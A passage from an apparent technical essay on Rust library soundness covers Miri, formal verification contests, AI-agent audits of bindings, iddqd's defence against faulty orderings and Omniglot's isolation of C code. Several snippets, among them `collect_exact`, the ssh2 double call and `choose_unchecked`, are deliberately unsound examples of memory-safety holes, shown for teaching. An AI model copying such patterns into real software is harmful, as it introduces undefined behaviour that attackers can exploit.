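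Ralf Jung (2017), announcing RustBelt on his blog, listed about ten verified library features and reported that the work had uncovered a real bug. He also acknowledged that the model was simplified. It omitted unwinding, the process by which a panicking program runs destructors; the full rules for when one thread's writes become visible to another, which later work added; and Rust's trait system, which has itself been a source of soundness bugs. Verifying a new library this way required a deep background in formal semantics, so most library authors rely on weaker evidence.

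### Miri and the aliasing models

Miri is an interpreter that runs a Rust program and stops if it detects undefined behaviour. It tracks which memory is still allocated, which bytes are initialised and whether threads race. A program that reads freed memory may print a plausible answer when compiled normally, but Miri reports the read.

It also checks the aliasing rules, which are harder to state. This program breaks them:

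```rust
let mut x = 1;
let p = &mut x as *mut i32;
let r = unsafe { &mut *p };
unsafe { *p = 2 };
*r = 3;
```

`p` is a raw pointer to `x`, and `r` is a mutable reference made from it. The fourth line writes through `p` while `r` is still in use. Compiled normally, the program will probably leave 3 in `x` without any visible error. But the compiler may assume that nothing else changes `x` while `r` is in use and optimise accordingly, for example by not rereading its value.

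Miri can check programs against two proposed models of these rules. For each memory location, Stacked Borrows keeps a stack of the pointers allowed to use it. Creating `r` from `p` puts `r` on top of `p`. Writing through `p` removes everything above it, including `r`, so the last line is undefined behaviour. Tree Borrows, a later model, uses a tree to record which pointer came from which, and writing through `p` disables `r`.

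Both models reject this program. If the fourth line only read from `p`, Stacked Borrows would still reject the last line, but Tree Borrows would accept it, because the program had not yet written anything through `r`. Rust has not officially adopted either model, so it is unsettled whether some code has undefined behaviour.

*Verifying the Rust Standard Library* (Cook, Delmas and colleagues, 2026) reports that Miri has found dozens of bugs in the standard library and is part of its routine testing. Miri's main weakness as evidence of soundness is that it checks only the executions it runs. A library's tests are clients its author thought of, and they mostly use the interface as intended. Miri would report no error for `frob_plain(0)`. It also runs C code only in an experimental mode, and doesn't check Rust's rules inside that code.

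### Verifying the standard library

The standard library matters more than any other because almost every client depends on it. It has about 34,000 functions, including 7,500 unsafe ones and another 3,000 that are safe to call but use unsafe code internally. Cook and colleagues count more than 74 soundness bugs that developers reported in the three years to March 2026.

Amazon started an effort in November 2024 to prove Rust's standard library free of undefined behaviour, and the Rust Foundation runs it as an open contest. *Lessons Learned So Far From a Community Effort* (Le Blanc and Lam, 2025) lists rewards of $5,000 to $25,000 for completing a challenge. Le Blanc and Lam calculated that about 4% of the unsafe functions and safe abstractions in `core`, the library's most basic part, had formal contracts for the main tool to check, though these contracts had not necessarily been proved.

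That tool is Kani, a model checker. An ordinary test calls a function with particular values, while a Kani test calls it with symbols that stand for every value of the right type. For a function of two 32-bit numbers, a single Kani test covers all 2⁶⁴ combinations. Kani follows loops up to a fixed number of repetitions and reports a failure if that number is too small. (People can also supply a loop invariant, which removes the limit.)

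Contributors wrote 725 of these tests by hand in sixteen months, and then progress levelled off. A program called Autoharness generated 16,748 more, of which 11,970 passed. Most of the passes, 10,194, were for safe functions with no unsafe code of their own. The 970 safe abstractions that passed, roughly a third of those in the library, are more relevant to soundness. Counting the handwritten tests, Kani verified 989 functions against formal contracts.

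Code that passes Kani's checks can still be unsound, because Kani doesn't check the aliasing rules or detect data races. It also doesn't check that functions preserve safety invariants, such as a vector's length never exceeding its capacity, so its checks don't cover the mistake in `evil`. Autoharness skipped 9,635 generic functions, which work with many types, because Kani needs a specific type to check them with. Nobody has completed the challenges for `Arc` and the other basic tools for sharing data between threads.

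One proof in the contest comes much closer to RustBelt's standard. It covers the library's doubly linked list and uses VeriFast, a tool based on separating conjunction. Under the proof's central predicate, the list owns every node from the first to the last, each in separate memory, so no node can appear twice and the list can't loop back on itself. The proof covers 19 functions directly and 5 more that only call those. It holds for any well-typed caller and a list of any length, although VeriFast doesn't yet check all the aliasing rules.

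The contest found mistakes in documentation and some missing `unsafe` annotations, but no previously unknown memory-safety vulnerabilities. Cook and colleagues credit the library's existing tests and Miri for the absence of new vulnerabilities, and the Rust Foundation's *How the Rust Standard Library Verification Contest Scaled Past Manual Proof Engineering* gives the same interpretation.

That now looks too optimistic. Bae (2026), in *Memory Safety Bugs in Rust Standard Library*, reports that Microsoft's FORGE Lab found several such bugs with an AI-powered scanner, and that safe code can trigger some of them. Bae traces the bugs to three mistaken assumptions: that code won't panic, that user-supplied implementations are correct, and that the underlying system behaves as expected.

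Trusting code not to panic is an easy mistake to make. Suppose a function copies an element out of a vector, passes it to the client's code, and then updates the vector's length. If the client's code panics, the function never updates the length. Rust then destroys the element twice, once as the copy and once as part of the vector. Bae had already led a project called Rudra, which targeted three bug patterns, one of them involving panics. Georgia Tech reports that Rudra scanned 43,000 Rust packages and found 264 previously unknown memory-safety bugs, two of them in the standard library.

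### Agents that write the hostile client

Finding a soundness bug often means writing a client that nobody has written before. AI agents, language models that can read files and write and run programs, are good at this. Davidoff (2026), in *The unreasonable effectiveness of LLMs for auditing Rust code*, reported dozens of issues in widely used libraries with the help of GPT-5.5. Momeu and Sen (2026), in *Agentic Discovery of Soundness Bugs in Safe Rust Bindings*, measured how well such agents find these bugs in bindings, Rust libraries that give safe access to C or C++ code.

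One of their examples is `ssh2`, which lets Rust programs use a C library, libssh2, to log in to other computers. Its `auth_methods` function returns text listing the ways in which a user may log in. A client can call it twice:

```rust
let methods = session.auth_methods("alice")?;
let again = session.auth_methods("alice")?;
println!("{methods}");
```

The text sits in a buffer that libssh2 frees on the next call, so the last line reads freed memory even though the client has no unsafe code. Appending to a vector while holding a reference to its first element is nearly the same mistake, but the compiler rejects that. It accepts both calls here because the binding's types don't express the C library's rule about the buffer.

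Momeu and Sen gave each agent the Rust code, the C code and a set of checking tools, including Miri and sanitizers, which add run-time checks to compiled programs. The agent looked for a rule that the types failed to enforce and tried to write a client that broke it. If the bug was in a safe interface, the client had to contain no unsafe code, which a one-line setting makes the compiler enforce. Agents could read the internet but not post to it. A person reviewed each finding before reporting it.

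They began with a controlled study of `git2`, a binding for the version-control library libgit2. Two models, Claude Opus 5.5 and the cheaper DeepSeek V4.1 Flash, carried out 24 audits with varying instructions. The audits produced 838 findings for $87. Many were duplicates, leaving 86 distinct defects, 36 of which were undefined behaviour. Another model, Claude Fable 5.2, judged the findings without being told their source and rated only one false.

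That figure deserves some caution because no person graded the findings, and the judge comes from the same company as one of the models it judged. Agents tried to rerun a random sample of 50 findings. Seventeen had no complete program to run, and 31 of the other 33 fully reproduced the stored result.

The instructions affected the quality of the evidence more than the accuracy of the findings. A finding was ready for a maintainer to accept if it described one real defect and included a recorded run to support it. Without rules for evidence, at most 51% of the findings in any group met this standard, compared with at least 74% with the rules. Agents seldom examined the contracts of unsafe functions unless the instructions mentioned them.

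Momeu and Sen worried that agents with a quota would invent bugs, so they tested this by asking agents for 25 new defects in `aws-lc-rs`, a cryptography library where earlier audits had found few. In each of the six audits, the agents reported one or two defects, none of them false, and stated that they had missed the target.

However, the audits missed many defects. Of the 51 `git2` defects that were not already public, 15 each turned up in only one of 24 audits. A single audit that finds nothing is therefore weak evidence that a library is sound.

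Momeu and Sen then audited 19 widely used Rust packages. Sixteen are bindings to code such as OpenSSL, SQLite and Google's V8 JavaScript engine, and three are programs or libraries that use the bindings. The agents found 213 bugs that cause undefined behaviour, 33 inadequate contracts and 23 cases in which a binding behaved differently from the code it wraps. A client can trigger 191 of the 213 bugs without writing unsafe code. In the other 22, the client uses some unsafe code but obeys every documented condition, so the library is still at fault.

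The most common causes were values that crossed the boundary between languages unchecked (65 bugs) and references that outlived their memory (56). Another 24 bugs involved threads. For example, `git2` let a client move a comparison of two file versions to another thread while the original thread kept using the same repository. The program ran normally, but a sanitizer detected a data race in all ten runs. Sixteen bugs break only the aliasing rules, and Momeu and Sen note that these don't corrupt memory with current compilers.

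Some bugs came from trusting the other language's documentation. According to V8's C++ declarations, a regular-expression search returns either an object or nothing, and the Rust binding relied on this. But when the pattern doesn't match, V8 returns a null value labelled as an object, and a safe client that treats it as an object crashes.

An audit of the Linux kernel's Rust interfaces took under two hours and found another 11 cases of undefined behaviour, as well as four inadequate contracts. Each requires kernel code that uses an interface in a particular way, and the audit didn't show that an ordinary program could trigger any of them.

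Momeu and Sen have reported 78 of the findings from the 19 packages to maintainers, who have fixed 24 and rejected none. The rest remain open. The maintainers' responses are better evidence than the judge's scores, since maintainers know the code and have little reason to accept a false report. The audits cost about $1,350 in total at list prices, excluding one whose cost was not recorded.

### Checking without running

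*UnsafeChecker* (Yin, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) is a program that analyses a library's code without running it. It tracks what owns each piece of memory, whether the data there is still usable, and whether pointers stay in bounds and correctly aligned. It reports a problem if a function might cause undefined behaviour itself or return something that lets safe code cause it later.

It caught a bug in `emap`, a library for storing values under numbered keys. To list the keys, the library copies each stored value to see whether a slot is occupied. If the value is a string, the copy points to the same characters as the original. When the function returns, Rust destroys the copy and frees the characters, but the map still holds the original string. The next client to look it up receives a reference to freed memory.

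On a benchmark of 46 known vulnerabilities, UnsafeChecker detected 32 and Rudra detected 11. UnsafeChecker also raised more false alarms, with only 64 of its 124 warnings correct, while all 11 of Rudra's were. Yin and colleagues also ran UnsafeChecker on Rust's public package registry and inspected the results for about 10,000 packages. Among 1,736 distinct warnings, they used Miri to confirm 114 new bugs in 83 packages. Developers or security experts have acknowledged 45, and maintainers have fixed 27.

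UnsafeChecker doesn't cover data races or the behaviour of C code, where Momeu and Sen's agents found many of their bugs. Yin and colleagues describe it as a bug-finding tool and don't claim that a library without warnings is sound.

### How far practice meets the definition

The definition of soundness assumes a correct compiler, and RustBelt's theorem covers λRust's typing rules, not the compiler that enforces Rust's. That compiler has soundness bugs, including one reported in October 2026 and described in *What the 11-year-old Rust borrow checker bug means* (Owen, 2026). Safe code can store a short-lived reference in a field declared to hold only long-lived data, and a destructor that relies on the declaration then reads freed memory. The Rust Project considers the bug a high priority but says that exploiting it takes deliberately malicious code.

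More followed in December, when Anthropic, which develops the Claude models, published *Finding logic bugs without general-purpose bug oracles* (2026). Faisal (2026) reports in *Claude Found a Seven-Year Bug in the Rust Compiler* that the researchers asked Claude to prove that safe Rust is type-safe, and that Claude produced dozens of counterexamples. One is a five-line safe program that reads freed memory because of a compiler bug more than seven years old. Such bugs don't make any library unsound, but they mean that a program built entirely from sound libraries can have undefined behaviour.

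Hardly any real Rust program has been proved to meet the standard. Such a proof would have to cover all the unsafe code the program depends on, and even the standard library is far from having one. Many popular bindings demonstrably fail to meet the standard.

The bug counts make Rust look worse than it is. Kobzol (2026), in *How memory safety CVEs differ between Rust and C/C++*, warns against comparing Rust's reported vulnerabilities with those of C and C++, because programmers assign blame for potential memory errors in libraries differently. If a C function corrupts memory when given a bad pointer, programmers blame the caller, but if a safe Rust function does so, they blame the function. Most of the bugs that Momeu and Sen report occur only when a client misuses the library in a specific way.

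In practice, the definition is most useful for showing that a library is unsound, because agents can now produce counterexamples with little effort. Establishing soundness still takes a proof, which is only as reliable as its model of Rust.

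## Sound wrappers around code that cannot be trusted

Rust's standard library includes `BTreeMap`, which stores values under keys and keeps the keys in order. It compares keys using code written by whoever defined the key type. That person implements the `Ord` trait, whose `cmp` method takes two keys and returns `Less`, `Equal` or `Greater`.

The answers should be consistent. If *a* comes before *b* and *b* comes before *c*, then *a* should come before *c*, and comparing the same two keys twice should give the same result. But the compiler only checks that `cmp` returns one of the three answers, so a programmer can write a `cmp` in safe Rust that ignores both keys and returns one at random.

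`BTreeMap` contains unsafe code, but safe code must not be able to cause undefined behaviour by using it. Rust's *How Safe and Unsafe Interact* explains that the map's unsafe code must therefore avoid undefined behaviour with every implementation of `Ord`, including inconsistent ones, even though the map requires `Ord` only because it needs a consistent order.

### A map with an inconsistent order

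In an example from the Rust users forum thread *How is BTreeMap written to be robust against Ord implementations*, the key type's `cmp` cycles through `Less`, `Equal` and `Greater`, in that order, whatever the keys are. A client inserts the values 1, 2 and 3 under three different keys.

The first insertion needs no comparison. The second makes one comparison, gets `Less`, and puts the second key before the first. The third gets `Equal`, so the map treats the third key as a repeat of the second and replaces the value 2 with 3. The client inserted three values and has two left, but no memory is corrupted. The map couldn't have detected the fault, because the two answers it got fit a valid order in which the second and third keys are equal and come before the first.

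More comparisons wouldn't make this dangerous. A B-tree keeps its keys in small blocks called nodes. A search goes through a node's keys from left to right and stops at the first one equal to or greater than the search key. Whatever `cmp` returns, the search stops either at a key in the node or after the last one. A wrong result can send the search to the wrong place in the tree but not outside it. A faulty order also can't break the code that manages the nodes' memory, because that code doesn't use `Ord`, as a participant in *Language vision regarding safety guarantees*, a thread on Rust's developer forum, points out.

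According to Rust's documentation, if a key's position in the order changes while the key is in a `BTreeMap`, the map may misbehave but won't cause undefined behaviour, and the effects stay within that map. The same is true of a hash map whose keys break the rules.

### An iterator that misreports its length

An iterator produces a series of items one at a time. Some iterators know how many items are left, and these can implement a trait called `ExactSizeIterator`, which has a `len` method. It is tempting to use `len` to fill a vector quickly. This function, adapted from an example by Paharia, belongs to the module of the simplified `Vector` type from earlier:

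```rust
pub fn collect_exact<I: ExactSizeIterator>(items: I) -> Vector<I::Item> {
    let n = items.len();
    let mut out = Vector::with_capacity(n);
    let mut i = 0;
    for item in items {
        unsafe { out.ptr.add(i).write(item) };
        i += 1;
    }
    out.len = n;
    out
}
```

The function reserves room for `n` elements and writes each item into the next place without checking that there is space. This works if the iterator's `len` is correct. But a client can write an iterator, entirely in safe Rust, that returns 0 from `len` and then produces three items. `collect_exact` writes all three into memory that the vector doesn't own.

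The length can also be too large. If `len` returns 5 and only three items arrive, the vector's length becomes 5, and a later call to `get(4)` reads memory that never held an element. The function can also leak memory, a bug that Paharia leaves as an exercise. If the iterator panics halfway through, `out.len` is still zero, so Rust never destroys the items already written. Leaks don't make a library unsound, however.

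A sound version counts the items as they arrive, allocates a larger block whenever the current one is full, and sets `len` to the number of items it wrote. It uses the reported length `n` only to decide how much memory to reserve at the start, so a wrong `n` only slows the function or wastes memory. Checking whether the block is full adds one comparison per item.

Rust's `Read` trait, for reading from files and network connections, has the same weakness. A faulty implementation can return the wrong count of bytes read, and unsafe code that relies on that count may treat uninitialised memory as data.

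### Every client and every behaviour

It helps to write the soundness criterion with a second quantifier. Let *B* be the behaviour of a component that library *L* calls, which covers what the component returns each time, whether it panics and whether it returns at all. Then *L* is sound if and only if

∀*C* ∈ SafeClients(*L*), ∀*B* ∈ Behaviours, ∀*r* ∈ Runs(*C* + *L* + *B*): ¬UB(*r*)

If the client supplies the component as safe Rust code, this is the original definition in a longer form, because "every safe client" already includes clients with strange `Ord` implementations. The longer form shows why such libraries are harder to get right. Someone reviewing `split_at_mut` can read every line that matters, and someone reviewing a vector can stop at the edge of its module. But the soundness of the careless `collect_exact` depends on `len` methods that nobody has written yet. Paharia considers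 this the hardest kind of unsafe Rust and recommends that library authors think like attackers.

A sound library doesn't have to allow for every possible implementation of everything it calls. `BTreeMap` also relies on the standard library's integers and slices, which have safe interfaces. Rust's guide justifies this by noting that each has one known implementation, maintained by the same people as `BTreeMap`, whereas trusting `Ord` would mean trusting every implementation that anyone writes.

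Other people's libraries fall in between. The opening post of *Language vision regarding safety guarantees* describes a hypothetical library `foo`, written entirely in safe Rust, and a library `bar` whose unsafe code needs `foo` to return correct results. An update to `foo` introduces an ordinary logic error, which causes undefined behaviour in a program that uses `bar`, and someone loses their bitcoins. The post attributes the problem to the language, because `foo`'s author has no way to keep `foo` out of other people's safety arguments.

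Another participant blames `bar`'s author, who should have reviewed one exact version of `foo` and accepted no other, or copied the code. This fits the criterion better, because a library that accepts future versions of `foo` is again relying on code that has not been written yet. Either approach is inconvenient, though, because `bar` no longer gets fixes to `foo` automatically. The same participant wants library authors to be able to declare that unsafe code may rely on a particular function's results, but Rust has no such feature for ordinary safe functions.

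### Unsafe traits

Whoever defines an unsafe trait documents its safety contract, and anyone who implements the trait has to write `unsafe impl` to declare that the implementation meets the contract.

Rust's *Trait ExactSizeIterator* warns that unsafe code must not rely on the length, because the trait is safe to implement, and refers readers to an unsafe trait called `TrustedLen`. Rust's contract for `TrustedLen` requires an iterator to produce exactly as many items as it reported, or else never reach the end. If `collect_exact` accepted only these iterators and used the length they guarantee, it could safely write without checking. The criterion becomes weaker, with *K* standing for the contract:

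∀*C*, ∀*B*, ∀*r*: *B* meets *K* ⇒ ¬UB(*r*)

If an iterator breaks the contract and corrupts memory, the fault lies with whoever wrote the `unsafe impl`, not with the author of `collect_exact`.

The `TrustedLen` contract excludes some iterators that look harmless, such as `Skip`, an adapter that leaves out the first few items. An iterator with more items than a `usize` can count reports the largest `usize` value as its minimum length and gives no maximum. If `Skip` drops ten of those items, there is no way to tell how many remain. `Skip` therefore does not implement `TrustedLen`, even when the iterator inside it does.

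`BTreeMap` could have required an unsafe version of `Ord`. The map's unsafe code could then have relied on every comparison, but anyone who defined a key type would have had to write `unsafe` and guarantee that the ordering was correct. Rust has traditionally avoided unsafe traits because they would spread unsafe code everywhere. According to Rust's guide, an unsafe trait is reasonable when the library can't be expected to guard against a bad implementation.

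Memory allocators are a good example. A program can replace the allocator that supplies all its memory by implementing `GlobalAlloc`, an unsafe trait. If the replacement hands out a block that is still in use, a vector's code can't detect the error. Thread safety is similar. A type that implements `Send` is safe to move to another thread, and one that implements `Sync` is safe for threads to share. Unsafe code can't check that no other thread is about to write to the same memory, the way it can check an index before using it. The compiler implements both traits automatically for types whose parts all implement them, so most programmers never have to write the promise themselves.

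Programmers who use `unsafe impl` to promise that a type is safe to send to another thread can get it wrong, and the compiler doesn't check the promise. The `futures` library had a lock guard that gave access to one part of a locked value. An `unsafe impl` declared the guard safe to send whenever the whole value was safe to send, without requiring the same of the part that the guard exposed.

### Two references to one record

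`iddqd`, the library of maps that Paharia wrote for the computer company Oxide, guards against incorrect orderings instead of requiring users to promise that their orderings are correct. Oxide uses it in the software that manages its server racks.

An ordinary map stores keys apart from values. A program that looks up users by email address must either keep a second copy of the address in each user's record, and risk the copies disagreeing, or pass the address and the record around together. `iddqd` reads the key from the record itself. Its ordered map, `IdOrdMap`, keeps the records in a list of numbered slots and has a separate B-tree that holds only slot numbers, sorted by their records' keys. When a client removes a record, the map frees its slot, and the next insertion uses the most recently freed slot.

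The unsafe code implements an iterator that lets a client go through the records in order and change them. Rust allows the client to collect all the iterator's mutable references and hold them at the same time. This is sound only if no two of them point to the same record, so the tree must never contain the same slot number twice. The borrow checker can't verify this because it treats each access as an access to the same list. The programmer has to verify it and then use unsafe code to override the compiler.

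If the order is consistent, the slot numbers never repeat. Paharia describes how a client could make them repeat without writing any unsafe code. Suppose a map holds five records with keys 0 to 4, in slots 0 to 4.

1. The client looks up key 0 and gets an entry, an object that remembers that the record is in slot 0.
2. The client changes how keys compare, so that `cmp` always returns `Equal`. It can do this if `cmp` consults a global variable, for instance.
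3. The client asks the entry to remove its record. The map searches the tree again, by key. If its first comparison is with key 2, the answer is `Equal`, so the map deletes slot number 2 from the tree. But it empties slot 0 in the list, because that is the slot the entry remembers.
4. The client restores the proper order and inserts a record with key 1000. The map puts the record in slot 0, which is now free, and adds 0 to the tree.

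| | Slot numbers in the tree | Occupied slots |
|---|---|---|
| At the start | 0, 1, 2, 3, 4 | 0, 1, 2, 3, 4 |
| After the removal | 0, 1, 3, 4 | 1, 2, 3, 4 |
| After the insertion | 0, 0, 1, 3, 4 | 0, 1, 2, 3, 4 |

The removal leaves an empty slot listed in the tree and makes the record in slot 2 unreachable, but it doesn't yet break the rule that the unsafe code depends on. After the insertion, the tree contains 0 twice, so a client that collects mutable references to all the records gets two references to the same one, which is undefined behaviour.

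The criterion makes no exception for unlikely clients. Nobody is likely to write this client on purpose, but an order that returned `Equal` at random could trigger the same bug.

The fix has two parts. When the map looks for a record whose slot number it knows, it now compares slot numbers whenever the keys compare as equal. In the example, the map is looking for slot 0 and reaches slot 2. The keys compare as equal, but 0 is less than 2, so the search continues to the left. The search can succeed only at the slot the map is looking for.

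But it might miss that slot, because the tree is in key order and slot numbers can be in any order. If the client had inserted the keys from 4 down to 0, key 4 would be in slot 0, and the tree would list the slots as 4, 3, 2, 1, 0. A search for slot 0 that started in the middle, at slot 2, would go left and find only slots 3 and 4. So if the search fails, the map now goes through the whole tree, comparing slot numbers and never calling `cmp`. This is slower, but it affects only clients with a faulty order.

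After the fix, the rule against repeated slot numbers depends on integer comparisons that `iddqd` makes itself. The client's ordering can still make the map slow or leave records in the wrong place.

### Testing against every ordering

Oxide checks `iddqd` in several ways because no single method covers both long sequences of operations and every possible ordering. One to three people have reviewed each piece of unsafe code, and a comment beside it gives the argument for its safety. Oxide also runs tests with deliberately broken orderings under Miri, using both Stacked Borrows and Tree Borrows.

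Other tests run random sequences of hundreds of operations and compare the results with those of a much simpler map that is slow but obviously correct. These tests are too slow to run under Miri, so they check directly, after every operation, that no slot number repeats. A variant gives each operation a random countdown that drops by one with each call to the client's code, which panics when the countdown reaches zero. This exposed several subtle bugs, some of which led to unsoundness.

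The language models Claude Opus 4.7 and GPT-5.5 found more problems by writing several kinds of client code that corrupted the map, including a memory allocator that panicked, which Paharia hadn't considered. Because models can produce convincing but false claims of unsoundness, Oxide has them write a test that makes Miri report undefined behaviour, then confirms that the test passes after the fix.

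None of these methods covers every ordering. When Paharia first wrote about the bug, formal tools couldn't help either. `iddqd` was too complicated for Kani, and Creusot couldn't prove facts that must hold even when the client's code misbehaves. Two weeks later, Paharia reported success with Soteria.

*Soteria* (Ayoun, Sjöstedt and Raad, 2025) describes a toolkit for symbolic execution, the technique Kani also uses, which runs a program on symbols instead of particular values. If a program fails unless a number *x* is greater than 5, the tool follows one branch for *x* > 5 and another for *x* ≤ 5, so two runs cover every number. Unlike Kani, Soteria's Rust version checks Tree Borrows, and it handles pointer-heavy data structures better. Ayoun and colleagues had an AI system write 72 tests of such structures so that their own knowledge of the tool wouldn't bias the choice. Soteria passed all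 72 in 6.6 seconds. With a limit of ten seconds per test, Kani passed 41, or 58 with extra hints about loops. It passed only two of the eight `BTreeMap` tests.

For `iddqd`, Oxide replaced the results of the client's comparisons with unknowns. Each time the program compares two keys, the answer can be anything, regardless of earlier answers, which covers correct orderings, constant ones and ones that change between calls. Soteria splits the run into branches only where the program's next step depends on the answer. It checks every branch for undefined behaviour and repeated slot numbers. The proof runs on the real B-tree, including its unsafe code. If Oxide removes either part of the fix, the proof fails.

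The proof covers only sequences of three operations, because longer sequences would be too slow for a check that Oxide runs routinely. The number of paths through a program can grow very fast. In one of Kani's tests, a loop that makes a decision for each bit of a 128-bit number has 2¹²⁸ paths, and Soteria timed out on it.

So the proof covers every ordering for short sequences, and the random tests cover some orderings for long ones. Both could miss a bug that needs four operations and a very unusual ordering. Ruling out such a bug would take a proof like the one for `Cursor`, showing that each operation preserves the rule in any map that already satisfies it. Soteria also doesn't detect every kind of undefined behaviour. Ayoun and colleagues ran it on 926 tests from the Kani and Miri projects, and in 77 it either missed an error or reported one that wasn't there. Oxide's *iddqd 0.4.6* accordingly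 calls the verification "bounded" and says that faulty client code "should never" cause undefined behaviour.

### Calling a C library

The client's ordering is safe Rust code, which limits the harm it can do to `iddqd`. It can give wrong answers, panic or run forever, but it can't write into the map's memory or return anything other than `Less`, `Equal` or `Greater`. A C library can write anywhere in the program's memory, return bytes that Rust considers invalid, or keep a pointer and use it later. Many of the bugs that Momeu and Sen found in bindings come from trusting C code not to do these things.

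*Building Bridges* (Schuermann, Toubes and colleagues, 2025) presents Omniglot, a system that lets Rust programs call existing C libraries without trusting or modifying them. One example is a C encryption function that returns a Boolean to indicate success. Many C programs represent Booleans as ordinary integers, so the function might return 2.

The Rust program puts the result in a `Message`, which is either encrypted, with a Boolean and a reference to some bytes, or unencrypted, with a string. As with `Option<bool>`, the compiler saves space by using one number for both the Boolean and the kind of message. A 0 or 1 means an encrypted message with that Boolean, and a 2 means an unencrypted message. If the C function returns 2 and Rust stores it as a Boolean, the program will later treat the message as unencrypted and the reference as a string that it owns. It may then read past the end of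 the bytes or free memory that it shouldn't.

Blocking the C library's access to Rust's memory wouldn't prevent this, because the Rust code itself makes the bad access. *Memory Safety is Merely Table Stakes* (Schuermann, Toubes and colleagues, 2025) uses a similar example to argue that isolating memory is only half the task.

Omniglot therefore gives the returned value a weaker type, one for which every pattern of bits is valid, and converts it to a Boolean only after a check. In simplified form:

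```rust
fn encrypt() -> Result<bool, BadValue> {
    match raw_encrypt() {    // returns a plain byte
        0 => Ok(false),
        1 => Ok(true),
        _ => Err(BadValue),
    }
}
```

Omniglot guarantees that the value is a valid Boolean, but not that it is correct. If the C function returns 2, the caller gets an error it can handle. But the value passes Omniglot's check if the function returns 1 even though the encryption failed.

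### Sharing memory with the library

Omniglot gives the C library a separate region of memory and uses the processor's memory protection to block access to everything else. If the library tries to read or write outside its region, the processor stops it, and the Rust program receives an error.

The Rust program and the library still have to exchange data, and copying everything would be slow, so the program reads and writes directly in the library's region. When the library returns a pointer, Omniglot treats it as a bare address that safe code can't use. It then checks that the address is correctly aligned and that the whole object lies inside the library's region. If both checks pass, the program may write to the object. Before the program can read the object as a particular type, Omniglot must also check that the bits are valid for that type.

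For some types, no such check is possible. The bits of a Rust reference, for example, don't show whether it is still valid. To let the library refer to a Rust object later, a program has to give it a stand-in, such as a number, and keep the object itself in Rust's memory.

A value that passed a check can also become invalid later. Suppose the library returns two overlapping pointers, one to an integer and one to a Boolean. If the program checks the Boolean and then writes 7 to the integer, the Boolean is no longer valid. Calling the library again could also invalidate the Boolean, since the library may change anything in its memory region.

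A lock could prevent this, but a program that used it wrongly would hang. Schuermann and colleagues use the borrow checker instead. Omniglot gives the program a token for each library. A checked value holds a shared reference to the token while the program uses the value, and writing to the library's memory or calling one of its functions requires a mutable reference to the same token. Rust doesn't allow both at once, so the compiler rejects a program that keeps using a checked value after something might have changed it, just as it rejected appending to `scores` while `first` was still in use. These checks happen during compilation and add no overhead when the program runs. A second token does the same for memory that the program might take back from the library.

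The tokens work only if the library stays idle while Rust code runs, so Omniglot must also stop the library from leaving threads running in the background. Schuermann and colleagues built two versions, but only the one for Tock, an operating system written in Rust for small devices, fully meets these requirements. In Tock, the library can't access the kernel's memory, start threads or make ordinary system calls, so the guarantee covers everything the library might do, including deliberate attacks.

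The Linux version relies on a processor feature that a malicious library can get around with system calls, and the library could also start threads. Developers have to rule out both, for instance by inspecting the library or blocking certain system calls. The Linux version protects against mistakes in the library but not against an attacker who controls it.

Both versions also assume that the processor, the Rust compiler and Omniglot's roughly 7,000 lines of code are correct. Neither prevents a library from inferring secrets from timing.

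### What isolation costs

Schuermann and colleagues measured the slowdown for six libraries, three on Tock and three on Linux. They compared ordinary unsafe calls with calls that only isolate the library's memory and with calls through the full system.

| Library and task | Cost of isolating memory | Further cost of Omniglot's checks |
|---|---|---|
| CryptoLib, computing an authentication code | 0.44% | 0% |
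| LittleFS, writing and reading a file | 20.1% | 0.5% |
| LwIP, answering a network packet | 52.1% | 3.4% |
| Brotli, compressing text | 0.6% | 0% |
| libsodium, hashing data | 3.4% | 0% |
| libpng, decoding an image | 12.7% | 0.8% |

Isolation accounts for nearly all the overhead, which depends mainly on how much work each call does. LwIP does so little with each small packet that switching in and out of the isolated region takes up a large share of the time, and it runs 57% slower under the full system than with unsafe calls. On Linux, an empty call takes about 99 nanoseconds, compared with 14 for an unsafe call. Sandcrust, an older system that runs the library in a separate process and copies data back and forth, takes about 11,000 nanoseconds.

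The time a check takes depends on the type. Any pattern of bits is a valid byte, so the compiler removes the check for raw bytes. For text, Omniglot must read every byte to confirm that the encoding is correct, which takes about 71 microseconds for 8 kilobytes on Linux.

Programmers also have to rewrite the code that calls the library, because Omniglot's interface differs from Rust's usual one. Schuermann and colleagues found this mostly mechanical. One exception was libpng, which handles errors by jumping out of several functions at once. Omniglot requires every function to return normally, so they had to write a small C wrapper for libpng.

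### Defend, demand a promise, or isolate

A library that calls code it can't trust has three options. The first is to defend against anything that code might do, as `BTreeMap` and `iddqd` do. This needs no cooperation from the code's author and often adds little to the running time, but it works only if the library can make every possible result harmless. A map can ensure that a wrong comparison merely leads to the wrong part of the tree, but a vector can't protect itself from an allocator that returns memory already in use.

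The library can use an unsafe trait to require a promise from whoever implements it. This avoids checking and covers cases where no defence is possible, but it helps only if that person can tell whether the promise is true. Someone who writes an iterator over a list can easily know how many items it will produce, but hardly anyone could honestly promise that a large C library never writes to the wrong address.

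Or the library can isolate the component and validate its results, as Omniglot does. Nobody has to understand the component or even have its source code. The guarantee then holds only if the isolation works and the library can check each result for whatever the program's safety depends on. The isolation may be weaker than it looks, as on Linux. The library can easily check that a byte is 0 or 1, but it can't tell from that byte alone whether the encryption succeeded.

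## What the guarantee means when the component is a learned model

A warehouse delivery cart can do five things: stop, go forward, go back, turn left and turn right. A network takes a picture from the cart's camera and returns a number, which the program uses to look up an action in a table. The network computes a score for each of the 256 numbers that fit in a byte, because its designers left room for more actions, and returns the number with the highest score. Training should teach it to return only 0 to 4, but another number might still score highest for some picture.

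Here are three ways to look up the action:

```rust
type Action = fn(&mut Cart);
static ACTIONS: [Action; 5] = [stop, forward, back, left, right];

pub fn choose_checked(net: &Network, image: &Image) -> Option<Action> {
    let n = net.run(image) as usize;      // 0 to 255
    ACTIONS.get(n).copied()
}

pub fn choose_unchecked(net: &Network, image: &Image) -> Action {
    let n = net.run(image) as usize;
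    unsafe { *ACTIONS.get_unchecked(n) }
}

pub fn choose_or_stop(net: &Network, image: &Image) -> Action {
    let n = net.run(image) as usize;
    let i = if n < ACTIONS.len() { n } else { 0 };
    unsafe { *ACTIONS.get_unchecked(i) }
}
```

`choose_checked` returns `None` if the number is 5 or more. It contains no unsafe code and is sound for every picture and every set of weights.

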